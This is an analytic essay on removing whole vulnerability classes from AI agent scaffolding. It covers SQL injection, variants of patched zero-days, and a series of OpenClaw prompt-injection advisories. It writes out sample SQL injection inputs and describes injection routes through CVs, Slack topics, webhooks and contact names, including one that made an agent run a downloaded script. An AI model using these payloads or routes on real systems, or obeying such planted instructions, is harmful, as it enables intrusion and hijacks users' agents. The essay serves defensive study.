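# Removing whole classes of vulnerability from AI agent scaffolding

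## How text from outside reaches an AI agent's model

An AI agent is a program that gives a task to a language model and carries out the steps in the model's output, such as searching the web, reading a file or sending an email. The model only takes in text (sometimes images) and produces text. Ordinary program code, called the scaffolding, does everything else, including gathering the model's input, running the tools, storing the memory and checking permissions. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (Kim, Liu and colleagues, 2026) defines agents as hybrid software with four components: one or more models, a memory of knowledge and past actions, tools that fetch information or change something, and the environment those tools work in, such as a browser or a company database.

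Zhang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes*, divide the scaffolding more finely. They audited the source code of agents that people install on their own computers, chiefly OpenClaw, an open-source assistant with hundreds of published security advisories. A prompt builder assembles the text for the model, and a parser turns the model's reply into something the program can act on. A tool dispatcher runs the tool that the model chose. A skill loader brings in add-on packages, a memory writer saves notes for later, a network client talks to outside servers, and a permission gate decides what may go ahead. On a local agent, all of these run with the full privileges of the person who started the program, so no internal barrier limits the damage from a mistake in one of them. The agent as a whole can also be unsafe even when each part does its own job correctly.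 For example, the researchers point out that vetting a skill gives little protection if the loader runs the skill's setup code before the permission gate has checked anything.

### One request through an agent

Suppose someone opens Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, in a project folder and types a request to add an architecture diagram to the README, the file that introduces the project to newcomers. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes what happens next.

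The request does not travel alone. Codex puts a good deal of text in front of it:

- general instructions for the model;
- the list of available tools, each with a description in plain English;
- a message about which folders the agent may write to and when it must ask permission;
- standing instructions that Codex collects from several places, among them a file called AGENTS.md in the project folder;
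- a note of the current folder and the user's command shell.

The user's sentence comes last. OpenAI's server then adds its own system message and sets the order of the opening items. The result is the model context, which is all the text and other input sent to the model in one call.

The model first replies with a request to run a command that prints the README. Codex runs the command, appends the output to the unchanged context and calls the model again with all of it. This loop repeats, possibly for hundreds of tool calls, until the model produces a message for the user instead of another tool request. If the user answers, Codex sends the entire history again, including the README. Codex replaces the history with a shorter substitute only when the conversation grows too long.

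Even this small job mixes text from several authors. OpenAI wrote some of the context and the user wrote some, but if the user downloaded the project from the internet, a stranger wrote the README. Untrusted text is any text that someone other than the developer or the authorised user can write or influence. It can arrive through tools as well as files. Codex users can connect outside tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard by which a separate server offers tools to an agent. Whoever runs that server can write the tool descriptions, and Bolin notes that a server can change its list of tools mid-conversation. Kim and colleagues count malicious tool names and descriptions as a separate attack from malicious web pages, because the harmful text arrives before the agent has fetched anything.

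An agent's memory can delay when outside text reaches the model. According to OpenClaw's *System prompt*, the program builds a fresh system prompt (the standing instructions at the head of the context) for every run. Unless it is running on top of Codex, it pastes in the contents of several files from the agent's workspace, including a long-term memory file. After a reset, it can also place recent daily notes ahead of the first message. A sentence that the agent copied from a web page into its memory on Monday can therefore reach the model on Thursday, in a different part of the context and without the web page it came from.

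### Message roles and trusted channels

To help the model tell these texts apart, the scaffolding labels each message with a role. OpenAI's *Model Spec* (2025), its public description of how its models should behave, defines five roles: system for messages from OpenAI, developer for the maker of the application, user for the person using it, assistant for the model's own replies, and tool for the output of a program. System messages have the most authority, followed by developer messages and then user messages. Assistant and tool messages have no authority by default, and neither do quoted passages, attachments or images in any message. The model should treat instructions in any of these as information about what the text contains.

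The default has exceptions because a user can delegate authority, sometimes implicitly. Someone who asks a coding agent to build a feature normally wants it to follow the project's AGENTS.md file. OpenAI tells the model to use judgment in such cases, trusting a file of that kind in the working folder more than a stray text file among the downloads, and a random web page not at all.

A trusted channel is any part of the context whose instructions the model is meant to follow. Trusted channels include the system prompt, tool descriptions and system events, which are short notices the scaffolding sends the model when a background job finishes or permissions change.

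The application assigns a role to each message that comes from outside the model, and its code can assign the wrong one. Developers can even send assistant messages that the model never produced. The roles are also coarse. OpenAI defines the user role as covering input from end users and also as "a catch-all for data we want to provide to the model". Codex, for example, sends the AGENTS.md instructions and the note about the current folder under the user role, though the user typed neither for that request.

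Software has to flatten all of this before the model can use it, because a language model takes a single sequence of tokens, which are words or pieces of words turned into numbers. Formatting code called the chat template writes the messages out one after another and inserts special markers to show where each speaker begins. Hugging Face's *Chat templates*, a guide to the company's library for running open models, describes two models built on the same base. One wraps each user message in a pair of instruction marks, while the other writes the name of the role before every message. Because conventions differ so much between model families, *The Self-Correction Illusion* (2026) lists the exact markers for each model tested.

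Training teaches a model to give more weight to text that follows a system marker. But the marker is part of the same sequence as the web page and the README, and the model has no separate input for commands. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, found that models infer who is speaking largely from how the text sounds, and that this tends to override the label when the two conflict.

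Outsiders can also try to type the markers themselves. OpenClaw encloses its own notices to the model between two fixed lines of text, and anyone who can send the agent a chat message could include the same two lines. The program therefore records each message's source separately from its text, and in new sessions it alters any lookalike lines in incoming text so that they no longer match. OpenClaw's developers call this prompt hardening and say it is not a guarantee against prompt injection. For rules that must hold, they direct operators to tool policies, approvals and sandboxes, which do not depend on the model following instructions.

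### Prompt injection

Prompt injection is text that gets a model to follow instructions its developer or user did not intend. David C's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published by Britain's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, gives the example of a recruiter's system that asks a model to score CVs against a job's requirements. One candidate hides a line in the CV telling the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the application. The recruiter meant the CV as data, but the model acts on part of it as a command. Security researchers call this indirect injection because the candidate never uses the recruiter's system. In direct injection, the attacker can add text to the user's own input.

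An injection can succeed because the model obeys text it should not trust, or because the scaffolding gives that text the wrong role. Suppose a web page's title contains an instruction to email the user's files to a stranger. If the scaffolding delivers the page as correctly labelled tool output and the model obeys the instruction anyway, the fault is in the model, not the scaffolding. If the scaffolding copies the title into a system message, it gives the instruction the developer's authority, and even a model that respected every role perfectly would obey. Programmers can find and fix this second fault like any other bug, but the fix does not make the model less likely to obey instructions in tool output.

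### Instance, variant and class

An older flaw shows what it means to remove a whole kind of bug. Many websites keep their records in a database and query it in a language called SQL. Imagine a shop whose staff search page builds its query by joining pieces of text:

```
"SELECT * FROM customers WHERE name = '" + name + "'"
```

Typing Smith into the search page brings up the customers called Smith. Typing `x' OR '1'='1` closes the quotation early, and the rest becomes part of the command. It adds a condition that is always true, so the database returns every customer. This attack is called SQL injection. A developer who learns of it might make the search page safe by adding code that doubles every quotation mark in the name, which is how SQL writes a quotation mark that belongs to the data.

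The developer has repaired one instance, a single bug at one place in the code. The shop's account page builds its query from a customer number, and numbers need no quotation marks:

```
"SELECT * FROM customers WHERE id = " + id
```

Typing `7 OR 1=1` works here, and copying the first repair across would change nothing, since the attack contains no quotation mark to double. The account page has a variant: a bug with the same root cause as the repaired one, reached by another path or a small change. The vulnerability class takes in every bug that breaks the same stated security rule, wherever it occurs and whether or not anyone has found it. For the shop, the rule is that the database must never execute what a visitor types. (MITRE's *CWE-1427*, the entry for prompt injection in a standard catalogue of software weaknesses, uses "class" differently, for a level of abstraction within the catalogue.)

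In a parameterised query, the program sends the command with a placeholder, `WHERE name = ?`, and sends the name separately. The database determines the command's structure without using the name, so the attacker's odd string only starts a search for a customer with an odd name. As David C puts it, the database engine can then never interpret the input as an instruction.

Parameterised queries alone don't help if a developer forgets to use them on a page. The shop can adopt a database interface that accepts only parameterised queries, with commands fixed in the source code, and rejects any command assembled while the program runs. A page where someone forgot to use a parameterised query then fails with an error instead of leaking records, and nobody has to know beforehand how many such pages there are. A parameter can stand for a value but not for a column name, so a page that lets staff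 choose how to sort the list needs a reviewed exception. David C dates the peak of SQL injection to around 2010 and credits its later rarity on websites to better defaults and better approaches, which arrived after a decade of break-ins. Prompts have no equivalent of the parameterised query, but developers still choose in code which channel each piece of text goes into.

### Source, sink and taint

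Finding the forgotten pages, or the forgotten routes into a system prompt, means following data through a program. Five lines from an imaginary agent are enough to show how:

```
1  page   = fetch(url)
2  title  = first_line(page)
3  notice = "Opened page: " + title
4  log(notice)
5  context.add(role="system", text=notice)
```

Line 1 is a source, a place where untrusted data enters the program, because whoever runs the website decides what `page` contains. Line 5 is a sink, a place where that data can do harm, because it writes to a trusted channel. Taint tracking marks `page` as tainted, then `title`, which line 2 cuts out of `page`, then `notice`, which line 3 builds around `title`. When a tainted value reaches line 5, the analysis reports a path from the source to the sink.

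Line 4 also receives tainted text, but that is harmless under the rule about trusted channels. Each rule has its own sinks, so Zhang and colleagues list them separately for each one. A log, for example, would be a sink under a rule against leaking passwords. For text that reaches the model, their sinks are the prompt builder and the memory writer. They include the memory writer because a saved note can come back as an instruction in a later session.

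A tool can track taint by analysing the code without running it. It can then cover paths that no test has exercised, but it may report paths that never occur in practice. Alternatively, the program can carry taint marks with the data while it runs. The marks then show what happened, but only on the paths the program took.

Some checks between source and sink make it safe to stop treating text as tainted. MITRE describes a chatbot that explains the difference between two entries in the CWE catalogue. The program inserts two entry numbers into a prompt, and an attacker adds instructions after the second. The fixed program accepts only "CWE-" followed by digits, so instructions can't get through. Page titles have no fixed format to check, and a filter for suspicious phrases would miss any wording its author hadn't anticipated.

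For the five-line program, the better repair is to change the role in line 5 from system to tool, but this closes only one path. The agent may also save the same title to memory as part of its browsing history and load it into the next day's system prompt, or another function may include the title in an error message that it reports as a system event. Neither path passes through line 5, so a test written for the original bug would pass with both still open. The developer still needs a way to find and close these other paths.

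## How often fixed bugs return as variants

Microsoft, Apple and Google have all released fixes that blocked one way of reaching a bug but left another, which attackers then found. Some of these bugs were zero-days, flaws that attackers exploit before a fix is available. In *A Year in Review of 0-days Exploited In-The-Wild in 2020*, Maddie Stone of Project Zero, Google's team of security researchers, found that six of the 24 zero-days discovered that year were closely related to flaws already public. For some of the six, the attacker only needed to change a line or two of code.

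The share was higher two years later. By mid-June 2022, Stone (2022) had counted at least nine variants among 18 zero-days. Google's *The Ups and Downs of 0-days* (2023) reports 17 variants among 41 zero-days for the whole year. Eight of the 17 were variants of bugs that attackers had exploited in 2020 or 2021.

Stone's *A Year in Review of 0-days Used In-the-Wild in 2021* gives no share of variants for the year in between. She considered only two of the 58 zero-days novel, one because the attack was so sophisticated and the other because it used only logic errors to escape a sandbox. The other 56 followed familiar patterns. Following a familiar pattern is a looser test than sharing a root cause, since two bugs can both involve memory that a program has already freed and have nothing else in common.

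Stone had no formal test for a variant either. She compared the code behind each pair of bugs and noted where she was unsure. One of the six from 2020 was in font-handling code that Apple and Microsoft had each copied from Adobe more than 20 years before. Microsoft had fixed a similar flaw in its copy, but Stone did not think it was clear whether anyone should have expected Apple to pick up the fix. She also doubted that attackers had exploited the Firefox bug on her list. At least two bugs on Google's 2022 list are not strictly variants, because later edits had undone the original fixes. One was in WebKit, the engine of Apple's Safari browser. WebKit's developers fixed it in 2013 and reintroduced it three years later.

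The 2022 share seems to be the last that Google published. *We're All in this Together* (Stone, Semrau and Sadowski, 2024) reported 97 zero-days for 2023, and *Look What You Made Us Patch* (Charrier, Sadowski and colleagues, 2026) reported 90 for 2025, but neither counted variants. The review of 2026 has not yet appeared. Google had also merged its records with those of Mandiant, a security company that had become part of Google, which raised the 2022 total from 41 to 62. The merged review did not classify the 21 extra bugs. If none of them was a variant, the share for 2022 would fall from 41% to 27%.

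Individual cases have continued. In November 2023 Microsoft patched a bypass of SmartScreen, the Windows feature that warns about suspicious files. The Zero Day Initiative's *ZDI Threat Hunting 2024* calls that patch "quite narrow". By December a group of attackers was using a new bypass against financial traders.

### The Internet Explorer chain

The longest chain on Stone's 2020 list is in JScript, an old engine that Internet Explorer used to run scripts in web pages. Its garbage collector frees the memory of objects that a script can no longer reach, so that the memory can be reused. To do this safely, the collector had to track every variable through which the script could still reach an object, but it missed some. An attacker could put an object in an untracked variable, delete every other reference to the object and start the collector. The collector would free the object's memory while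 the script could still use it, and the attacker could then fill that memory with other data.

Five bugs in JScript broke the same rule in different places. The rule could be broken when JScript ran a function supplied by the script during a built-in operation, such as sorting a list. The CVE numbers below come from the public catalogue of known vulnerabilities.

| Bug | Came to light | What the collector failed to track | Operation that ran the attacker's function |
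|---|---|---|---|
| CVE-2018-8653 | December 2018 | the special variable `this` | testing an object's prototype |
| CVE-2019-1367 | September 2019 | entries in the function's `arguments` list | sorting a list |
| CVE-2019-1429 | November 2019 | entries in the `arguments` list | converting an object to JSON text |
| CVE-2020-0674 | January 2020 | the function's named arguments | sorting a list |
| CVE-2020-0968 | April 2020 | a temporary value | adding two objects together |

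Microsoft's patch for the first bug left the `arguments` list untracked. After its patch for the second, the script that demonstrated the bug still worked on a patched machine. In November 2019 Microsoft released another patch, which stopped that script and closed the path through JSON conversion.

But a JScript function can refer to the same input as `arguments[0]` or by a name such as `arg1`, and the collector still did not track the names. Replacing `arguments[0]` with `arg1` made the old script work again. After Microsoft fixed that, one more untracked value remained, which JScript created while adding two objects. Microsoft listed this last bug as exploited, then withdrew the label the next day.

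Google attributed the other four exploits to a single attacker, who used the same technique each time to turn the bug into an attack. Stone argues that a comprehensive fix at the start would have made the attacker work harder or look for a different bug. Microsoft instead fixed the collector one or two places at a time, and after each fix the attacker still had most of a working exploit.

### The Windows pair

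The second chain is in win32k, the part of the Windows kernel that manages windows on the screen. The kernel is the core of the operating system and controls everything else on the machine. A program can ask for extra memory for each of its windows, and the kernel records where that memory is. It stores the location either as an ordinary address in the program's own memory or as an offset, the distance from the start of a block of kernel memory. A flag records which of the two it is.

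Jin, in *CVE-2021-1732*, describes how an attacker could get the flag and the note to disagree:

1. The attacker's program asks the kernel to create a window with extra memory.
2. The kernel calls back into the program so that the program can allocate the memory.
3. During this callback, the program calls another Windows function that changes the note to an offset and turns on the flag.
4. The program ends the callback and returns any number it likes.
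5. The kernel writes that number over the note but leaves the flag on, so it treats the attacker's number as an offset into its own memory.

The attacker can then read and change kernel memory, and can use this to give the program the highest privileges on the machine.

In February 2021 Microsoft patched the code path that triggers the callback when a window is created. Other parts of the kernel, including those that handle menus and tooltips, could also trigger it, and by January 2022 attackers were using them. The two bugs are so alike that RyeLv, in *CVE-2022-21882*, tells them apart by which kernel function made the call.

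Microsoft's second patch changed the function that performs the callback so that it checks the flag just before finishing and reports failure if the flag is on. The check now applies to every caller, including any that the developers have not thought of. Jin had suggested auditing every Windows function that can change such a flag during a callback, which might have uncovered the second bug sooner.

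### Root cause, variant and patch analysis

Google calls a patch complete if it is correct and comprehensive. A correct patch leaves no way to exploit the bug it addresses, and a comprehensive patch applies the fix everywhere it is needed. Microsoft's September 2019 patch for JScript was not correct, because the original attack still worked. Microsoft's first win32k patch blocked the original attack but was not comprehensive. Stone recommends several kinds of analysis to catch both failures.

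Root cause analysis means finding the underlying mistake, not just the steps one attacker took. FreeType, a library that many programs use to draw fonts, shows the difference. Some fonts contain small images, and FreeType uses each image's width and height to calculate how much memory to set aside. In 2014 a Project Zero researcher reported that a very large image could make this calculation overflow, so that FreeType set aside too little memory. The developers added a check that rejected large images.

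But the file stores each dimension as a 32-bit number, and FreeType shortened it to 16 bits before the check. This turned a width of 65,537 into 1, so an enormous image could pass the check. FreeType then copied the whole image into memory sized for the shortened dimensions. Attackers exploited this in 2020. In their second fix, the developers applied the same limit to the original dimensions, before FreeType shortened them. Stone points out that putting the check there in 2014 would have prevented both bugs.

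Variant analysis means looking for the same mistake elsewhere. Researchers can read through related code, write code queries based on the known bug, or adjust their fuzzers, which test programs with large amounts of odd input, to find out why they missed it. In 2020, attackers exploited a bug in the kernel that iPhones and Macs share. By December, Tielei Wang and Xinru Chi had used variant analysis to find a close variant. Apple fixed it in test versions of its next releases, and Wang and Chi presented their work in April 2021. Attackers still used the variant that year, with the technique from the presentation, against Macs running an older system that had not yet received the fix.

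Patch analysis means comparing a repair with the root cause, ideally before release. In February 2020 Sergei Glazunov of Project Zero re-examined a Chrome patch from November 2019. The bug involved loops whose counter could stop being a valid number. Chrome's developers had added a check based on the counter's starting value and step size, but a script could change the step size while the loop was running. Changing a couple of lines made the old attack work again. Chrome's next patch fixed this but introduced a different vulnerability. Stone encourages companies to show a planned patch to the person who reported the bug, who may notice gaps in it.

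Stone also recommends studying the attacker's technique, so that developers can block the method as well as the bug. All this work takes time, and users remain exposed until the patch comes out. She acknowledges that speed and completeness can conflict.

AI models can write patches quickly, but those patches need the same analysis. 1Password's *How information quality impacts LLMs' ability to patch complex, novel vulnerabilities* describes a test on six recent vulnerabilities that needed complex fixes. Only 26.0% of the patches removed the flaw without changing how the program behaved or weakening its security in some other way. The company chose hard cases and gave the models some inaccurate information, so the result is weak evidence about easier repairs.

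### How often a patch leaves something behind

Google's 41% is the share of exploited zero-days that were variants, not the share of patches that leave a variant. Suppose developers release 1,000 patches in a year and attackers exploit 40 zero-days, 16 of which are variants of bugs those patches fixed. Variants make up 40% of the zero-days, yet at most 16 of the 1,000 patches, or 1.6%, led to an exploited variant. Many more than 16 might have left a variant that no attacker found or needed, but their number can't be calculated from the share among zero-days.

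The zero-days are also an unusual sample, because Google can count only those that somebody detected and disclosed. Stone asks whether defenders keep seeing familiar bugs because they know how to detect those. If attacks that use a new kind of bug are more likely to go unnoticed, the true share of variants is lower than the published one. Google suggests that the rise since 2020 probably comes from a mixture of causes, which could include better detection, better recognition of variants, more use of variants by attackers and less thorough patches. Chance could also explain much of the rise, since there were only 24 bugs in one year and 41 in the other.

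The products in the sample matter too. Of the 17 variants in 2022, seven were in browsers and six in operating systems. The remaining four were in business products: a firewall, the Confluence collaboration software and Microsoft's Exchange mail server, which had two. But Charrier and colleagues found that browsers accounted for less than 10% of zero-days in 2025, while business software and equipment accounted for 48%. Nobody has shown that variants are as common in the newer mix of products.

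Similar caution applies to Stone's estimate that better patching and testing could have prevented at least half the zero-days of early 2022. Better patches would have removed those bugs, but some of the attackers might have found others. Stone argues that starting again is harder for them.

In *Why Not Fix It Once and for All?*, Qi, Li and Wang (2026) collected 25,113 vulnerabilities in open-source software for which the public catalogue links to a patch. For 1,646 of them, the catalogue links to more than one patch, and the researchers examined all of these by hand. The most common reason, found in 830 cases, was the harmless one that developers had to repeat a repair in several versions of a program or in related projects. In 641 cases, however, the first patch had not fully removed the vulnerability, and in 119 a patch had introduced a new bug.

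The 641 incomplete repairs are about 2.6% of all the vulnerabilities in the collection. One was in XFS, a Linux file system, where a number read from disk could be too large. The first patch rejected values above a maximum, but the program stored the number in a form that allowed negatives, so a sufficiently large value became negative and passed the check. The developers fixed this 18 days later.

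The real rate is probably higher than 2.6%, because the researchers could see a follow-up patch only if the catalogue listed it under the same CVE number as the original. Each bug in the JScript and win32k chains has its own CVE number, so a similar chain in an open-source project could look like a series of separate, successful repairs.

Li and Paxson's *A Large-Scale Empirical Study of Security Patches* (2017) covers more than 4,000 fixes in 682 open-source projects. Liu, Zhang and colleagues, in *Characteristics, Root Causes, and Detection of Incomplete Security Bug Fixes* (2025), cite that study as finding that 12% of fixes were incomplete. They also count a fix as incomplete if it introduces a new flaw, so the 12% is not directly comparable with the 2.6%.

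Liu and colleagues then examined 26 incomplete fixes in the Linux kernel. They found them mainly by searching bug databases for the words "incomplete" and "incorrect", so the sample can show why fixes fail but not how often. Some developers had fixed the symptom of a crash without understanding its cause. Others had understood the cause but overlooked the same mistake in similar code. For example, one patch corrected several file systems but missed tmpfs, which keeps its files in memory. Still others made a new mistake while writing the fix. Most of the incomplete fixes took 50 to 200 days to be discovered, though one mistake in a variable name went unnoticed for 1,564 days.

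The overlooked cases most closely resemble the variants on Google's lists, and a tool can help find them. Liu and colleagues compared the patterns of known repairs across 1,615 kernel vulnerabilities and found two incomplete fixes that nobody had reported.

A higher figure comes from the Zero Day Initiative, which buys bugs from independent researchers and reports them to the companies responsible. Its spokesman Dustin Childs told Hurley (2022) that 10% to 20% of the bugs it bought resulted from faulty or incomplete patches. Like Google's figure, this is a share of bugs, not patches. People who sell bugs also have a reason to study new patches, because a patch shows where a program was recently weak.

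The programme responded by giving companies less time to fix such bugs before it publishes the details. *New Disclosure Timelines for Bugs Resulting from Incomplete Patches* (Gorenc, 2022) sets deadlines of 30, 60 or 90 days instead of the usual 120, depending on the severity of the bug and how much protection the first patch gave.

These figures justify searching the code around a repaired bug, because the attacker who exploited JScript needed only small changes to get from one bug to the next. Developers can't use the figures to calculate the odds that a particular patch has left a variant. Most of the evidence comes from browsers, operating systems and other established software, so agent code needs to be studied separately.

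## How the same flaws recur in AI agents

The fullest public record of one flaw recurring in an AI agent comes from OpenClaw. The table lists ten cases from 2026 in which OpenClaw gave outside text too much authority or passed it to the model without marking it as outside text. OpenClaw numbers its releases by date, so version 2026.2.3 is from early February.

| Fixed in | Outside text | Where it ended up | Severity | Repair |
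|---|---|---|---|---|
| 2026.2.3 | topic or description of a Slack channel | system prompt | 3.7, low | take it out of the system prompt |
| 2026.2.13 | headers from a program trying to connect | log that the model might read | 3.1, low | clean and shorten the headers |
| 2026.2.13 | messages from another session | user messages | 8.6, high | record and show where each message came from |
| 2026.2.15 | name of the working folder | system prompt | 8.6, high | strip line breaks and invisible characters |
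| not listed | title or address of a linked resource | prompt text | medium | not listed |
| 2026.4.8 | text sent to the "wake" webhook | trusted system event | 7.8, high | treat it as an untrusted event |
| 2026.4.8 | output of background commands | trusted system event | 7.3, high | lower the trust of the output |
| 2026.4.10 | names supplied with webhook requests | trusted system event | 9.3, critical | clean the name and mark the event untrusted |
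| 2026.4.20 | output of scheduled jobs | trusted system event | 6.3, medium, or 1.7, low | keep the untrusted label |
| 2026.4.23 | shared contacts and locations | the user's message | no score | move the text to a separate untrusted block |

### From channel topics to folder names

In Slack, a workplace chat service, each channel has a topic and a description that ordinary members can often edit. NVD's *CVE-2026-24764 Detail* (2026), an entry in the US government's vulnerability database, describes how OpenClaw could copy both into the system prompt. Anyone able to edit either could then give the model text that appeared to come from the agent's developers. According to GCVE's *GHSA-782p-5fr5-7fj8* (2026), if the agent could run tools, a successful injection might make it run one the user never asked for or reveal private data.

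The path through the log was less direct. A program that connects to OpenClaw sends headers, short pieces of text that identify it. According to GitLab's *GHSA-g27f-9qjv-22pm* (2026), OpenClaw wrote some of these headers to its log without cleaning them or limiting their length, even when the program had not logged in. A stranger could therefore plant text in the log and wait for the agent to read it while investigating a problem for the user. Eye Security, the company that tried this attack, could not reliably get the model to obey the planted text, and in one test the agent warned the user about it. Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-22438* (2026) gives the flaw a score of 3.1.

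The same release changed how OpenClaw handles messages between sessions, which are separate conversations that can run at the same time. An agent in one session can send a message to an agent in another. Model providers expect user and assistant messages to alternate, so OpenClaw stored the incoming message under the user role. Miggo's *GHSA-w5c7-9qqw-6645* explains that nothing then distinguished it from a message the user had typed. For example, a web page that hijacked a research agent could use it to give an agent with email access orders that seemed to come from the user. *The Whisper Game* (CVE Reports, 2026) scores this flaw 8.6.

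OpenClaw's developers kept the user role but added a record of each message's origin. Messages from other sessions now reach the model with a short label, and the memory feature no longer saves them as the user's own words. The program accepts only three values for the origin: an outside user, another session or the system itself (Suwansathit, Zhang and Gu, 2026, *A Security Analysis of the OpenClaw AI Agent Framework*).

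Two days later, OpenClaw fixed a flaw in how it copied the name of the agent's working folder into the system prompt, according to OSV's *GHSA-2qj5-gwg2-xwc4* (2026). Folder names can contain line breaks and invisible characters, so an attacker could end the line about the folder and start what looked like a new instruction. OpenClaw now removes those characters, but ordinary words in a folder name still reach the system prompt, so anyone who shares a project can put a phrase there.

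OpenClaw also pasted the titles and addresses of linked resources straight into prompt text. Cybersecurity Help's *Code Injection in OpenClaw* (2026) rates this as a medium-severity flaw that an attacker can exploit remotely, and recommends installing the developers' update.

### Four paths into system events

OpenClaw shows the model its trusted system events on lines that begin with "System:". In April 2026 the developers closed four paths into these events within two weeks.

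One path began with a webhook, a web address to which another program can send a message when something happens. A user might have a mail service notify OpenClaw whenever an email arrives. GitLab's *GHSA-jf56-mccx-5f3f* (2026) describes how OpenClaw's wake webhook turned the notification into a trusted system event. The mail service had to supply a secret token, but the token only proved that the notification came from the service. If the notification included the email's subject line, anyone who emailed the user could write part of a trusted system event.

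Another path started with commands that OpenClaw runs in the background. When one finishes, the model gets a notice, which can include the command's output. According to OSV's *GHSA-gfmx-pph7-g46x* (2026), the developers had meant OpenClaw to lower the trust level of these notices, but it skipped that step for commands run on the local machine. Version 2026.4.8 fixed both this flaw and the one in the wake webhook.

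The agent webhook, which starts a separate run, accepts a name, such as "Email", with each request. OpenClaw could put that name into a trusted system event. OSV's *CVE-2026-43534* (2026) scores this flaw 9.3, the highest in the series. Version 2026.4.10 cleans the name and marks the whole event as untrusted, according to GCVE's *GHSA-7g8c-cfr3-vqqr*.

Ten days later, the developers fixed a flaw in how OpenClaw reported scheduled jobs that a webhook had started. OpenClaw sent each job's output to the main conversation without the setting `trusted: false`, according to Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-37320* (2026). Because the program treated any event without that setting as trusted, every function that handled outside text had to pass the setting along.

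Two Slack flaws had already let outside text reach system events. GitLab's *GHSA-x2ff-j5c2-ggpr* (2026) describes one in which an unauthorised member of a shared workspace could add such text through an interactive feature of a message. In the other, someone not on the approved sender list could trigger events by editing or deleting a message. CERT.hr's *CVE-2026-32895* (2026) lists 2026.2.26 as the version that fixed this. Both entries describe the mistake as a missing check on the sender, so a developer who searched only past prompt injection reports could easily have overlooked them.

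### Contacts and locations

The last case in the table involves contacts and locations shared in chat apps. When a user forwarded a contact to OpenClaw, the program inserted the contact's name and number into the user's message between angle brackets. A contact's name can contain angle brackets, so the model had no reliable way to tell where the name ended. Imperva's *Compromise OpenClaw with Prompt Injections in Message Objects* reports attacks through contacts, vCards (files that hold contact details) and the labels of shared locations. Chat apps truncate long contact names on screen, so the user could forward an instruction in the name without seeing it.

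When Imperva, a security company, tested the attack on Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro, the agent downloaded and ran a harmless script from the researchers' server. The same instruction failed when it was hidden in an image. Imperva suspects that developers have trained models against that better-known trick. It gives no success rate for either method.

OpenClaw already put warning markers around text it fetched from the web, but not around contacts or locations. Version 2026.4.23 moves contact names, vCard fields and location labels into a separate block for untrusted information. The model may still follow an instruction in that block, but the instruction no longer looks like part of what the user wrote.

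### Why the scores differ so much

The scores use CVSS, a standard scale from 0 to 10 that combines how easily an attacker can exploit a flaw with how much damage could follow. Slack topics and folder names both reached the system prompt, yet the Slack flaw scored 3.7 and the folder flaw 8.6. The Slack score is based on a difficult attack with limited damage, while the folder score is based on an easy attack with severe damage. The folder score also uses a newer version of the scale. Neither score measures how often a model would obey the text.

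The Slack score of 3.7 appears in Lutra Security's *OpenClaw has Remote Code Execution via System Prompt Injection* (2026). Remote code execution, which means running programs on someone else's machine, would normally get a far higher score.

The flaw in scheduled jobs has three severity scores. OSV's *CVE-2026-44999* (2026) lists 6.3, and a withdrawn duplicate listed 5.3. The advisory that Positive Technologies reproduces gives 1.7, on the grounds that a wrong label does not by itself get an attacker past the login, the tool policy or the sandbox.

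Such scores are a poor guide to which bugs deserve a search for variants. A team that searched for variants only of severe bugs would have fixed the Slack topics bug and stopped, leaving the more highly rated paths open.

### Which paths already existed

A later flaw in the series could be a missed sibling, meaning a path that was already open when the developers fixed Slack. It could also be a new mistake in code written afterwards, or a regression, where a later edit undid an earlier fix.

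The wake webhook is a missed sibling. OpenClaw's *Webhooks* (2025), dated 24 December 2025, described it about six weeks before the Slack repair. The documentation's example message is "System line", so the developers seem to have intended outside programs to write system events. They changed that design only in April. The code did what the documentation described, so searching for differences between the two would not have found this flaw.

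The hook-name flaw was probably a missed sibling too. A Chinese copy of the *Webhooks* page, stored on 5 February 2026, already shows a name field in requests to the agent webhook, but it doesn't show whether OpenClaw was then putting the name into trusted events. OSV lists every version back to 0.1.0 as affected, but only because its entry doesn't specify which version introduced the flaw.

The background commands lacked a protection that the developers had already designed, though it is unclear whether the protection came before or after the Slack repair. For scheduled jobs, the published descriptions are consistent with either old code that was never updated to pass on the trust setting or new code that dropped it.

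The flaws in logs, session messages and folder names were all fixed within twelve days of the Slack repair. It is unlikely that all three arose in that time, but their advisories give no starting version. The contact flaw has no known starting date either, and none of the descriptions suggests a regression. OpenClaw's code is public, so anyone could settle the open cases by checking the version just before the Slack repair for each later path.

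The same piece of text can also cause a different kind of flaw. In July 2026, GitLab's *GHSA-6c4r-g249-wv3c* (2026) described how OpenClaw revealed the real location of the user's workspace to an agent in a sandbox. That path went into a prompt, as the folder name had in February. But this flaw is not a variant of the earlier one, because it broke a rule about secrecy by giving the agent information it should not have.

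### One mistake across many chat apps

Suwansathit and colleagues classified 470 OpenClaw advisories filed between 31 January and 15 April 2026, but much of their detailed analysis describes an earlier set of 190 from February. One group of 13 advisories in that earlier set concerns the code that decides whose messages the agent should accept.

An OpenClaw user can restrict the agent to a list of approved senders. In this group of flaws, OpenClaw checked the list against a name that senders could change. Nextcloud Talk, for example, gives each account a permanent ID and a display name, and OpenClaw accepted a match on either. If the user approved the account with the ID `alice`, anyone could change their display name to "alice" and give the agent orders. OpenClaw then treated the attacker's messages as having an approved sender's authority, even if it labelled everything else correctly.

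A similar problem arose with Telegram usernames, which one person can give up and another can claim. OpenClaw's developers had a test confirming that the agent would accept an approved username, and it passed because the code did what they intended. To fix the flaw, they required Telegram's permanent numeric IDs and changed the test to check that a username alone is not enough. They also wrote a tool that looks up the IDs for usernames already on people's lists.

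For Nextcloud Talk, the developers removed the display name from the function that checks the list and removed "name" from the kinds of match it can report. Any code that still expects a name match now causes an error before the program runs, which helps developers find leftover uses of the old rule.

The code for each chat app checked identity separately. Suwansathit and colleagues argue that one shared function, written and checked once, would have prevented all 13 flaws. That is convincing for the flaws involving display names and usernames, but the 13 may not all be the same kind of mistake. According to GitLab's summary of an iMessage flaw, apparently one of the 13, OpenClaw let people approved for private messages give it orders in groups as well.

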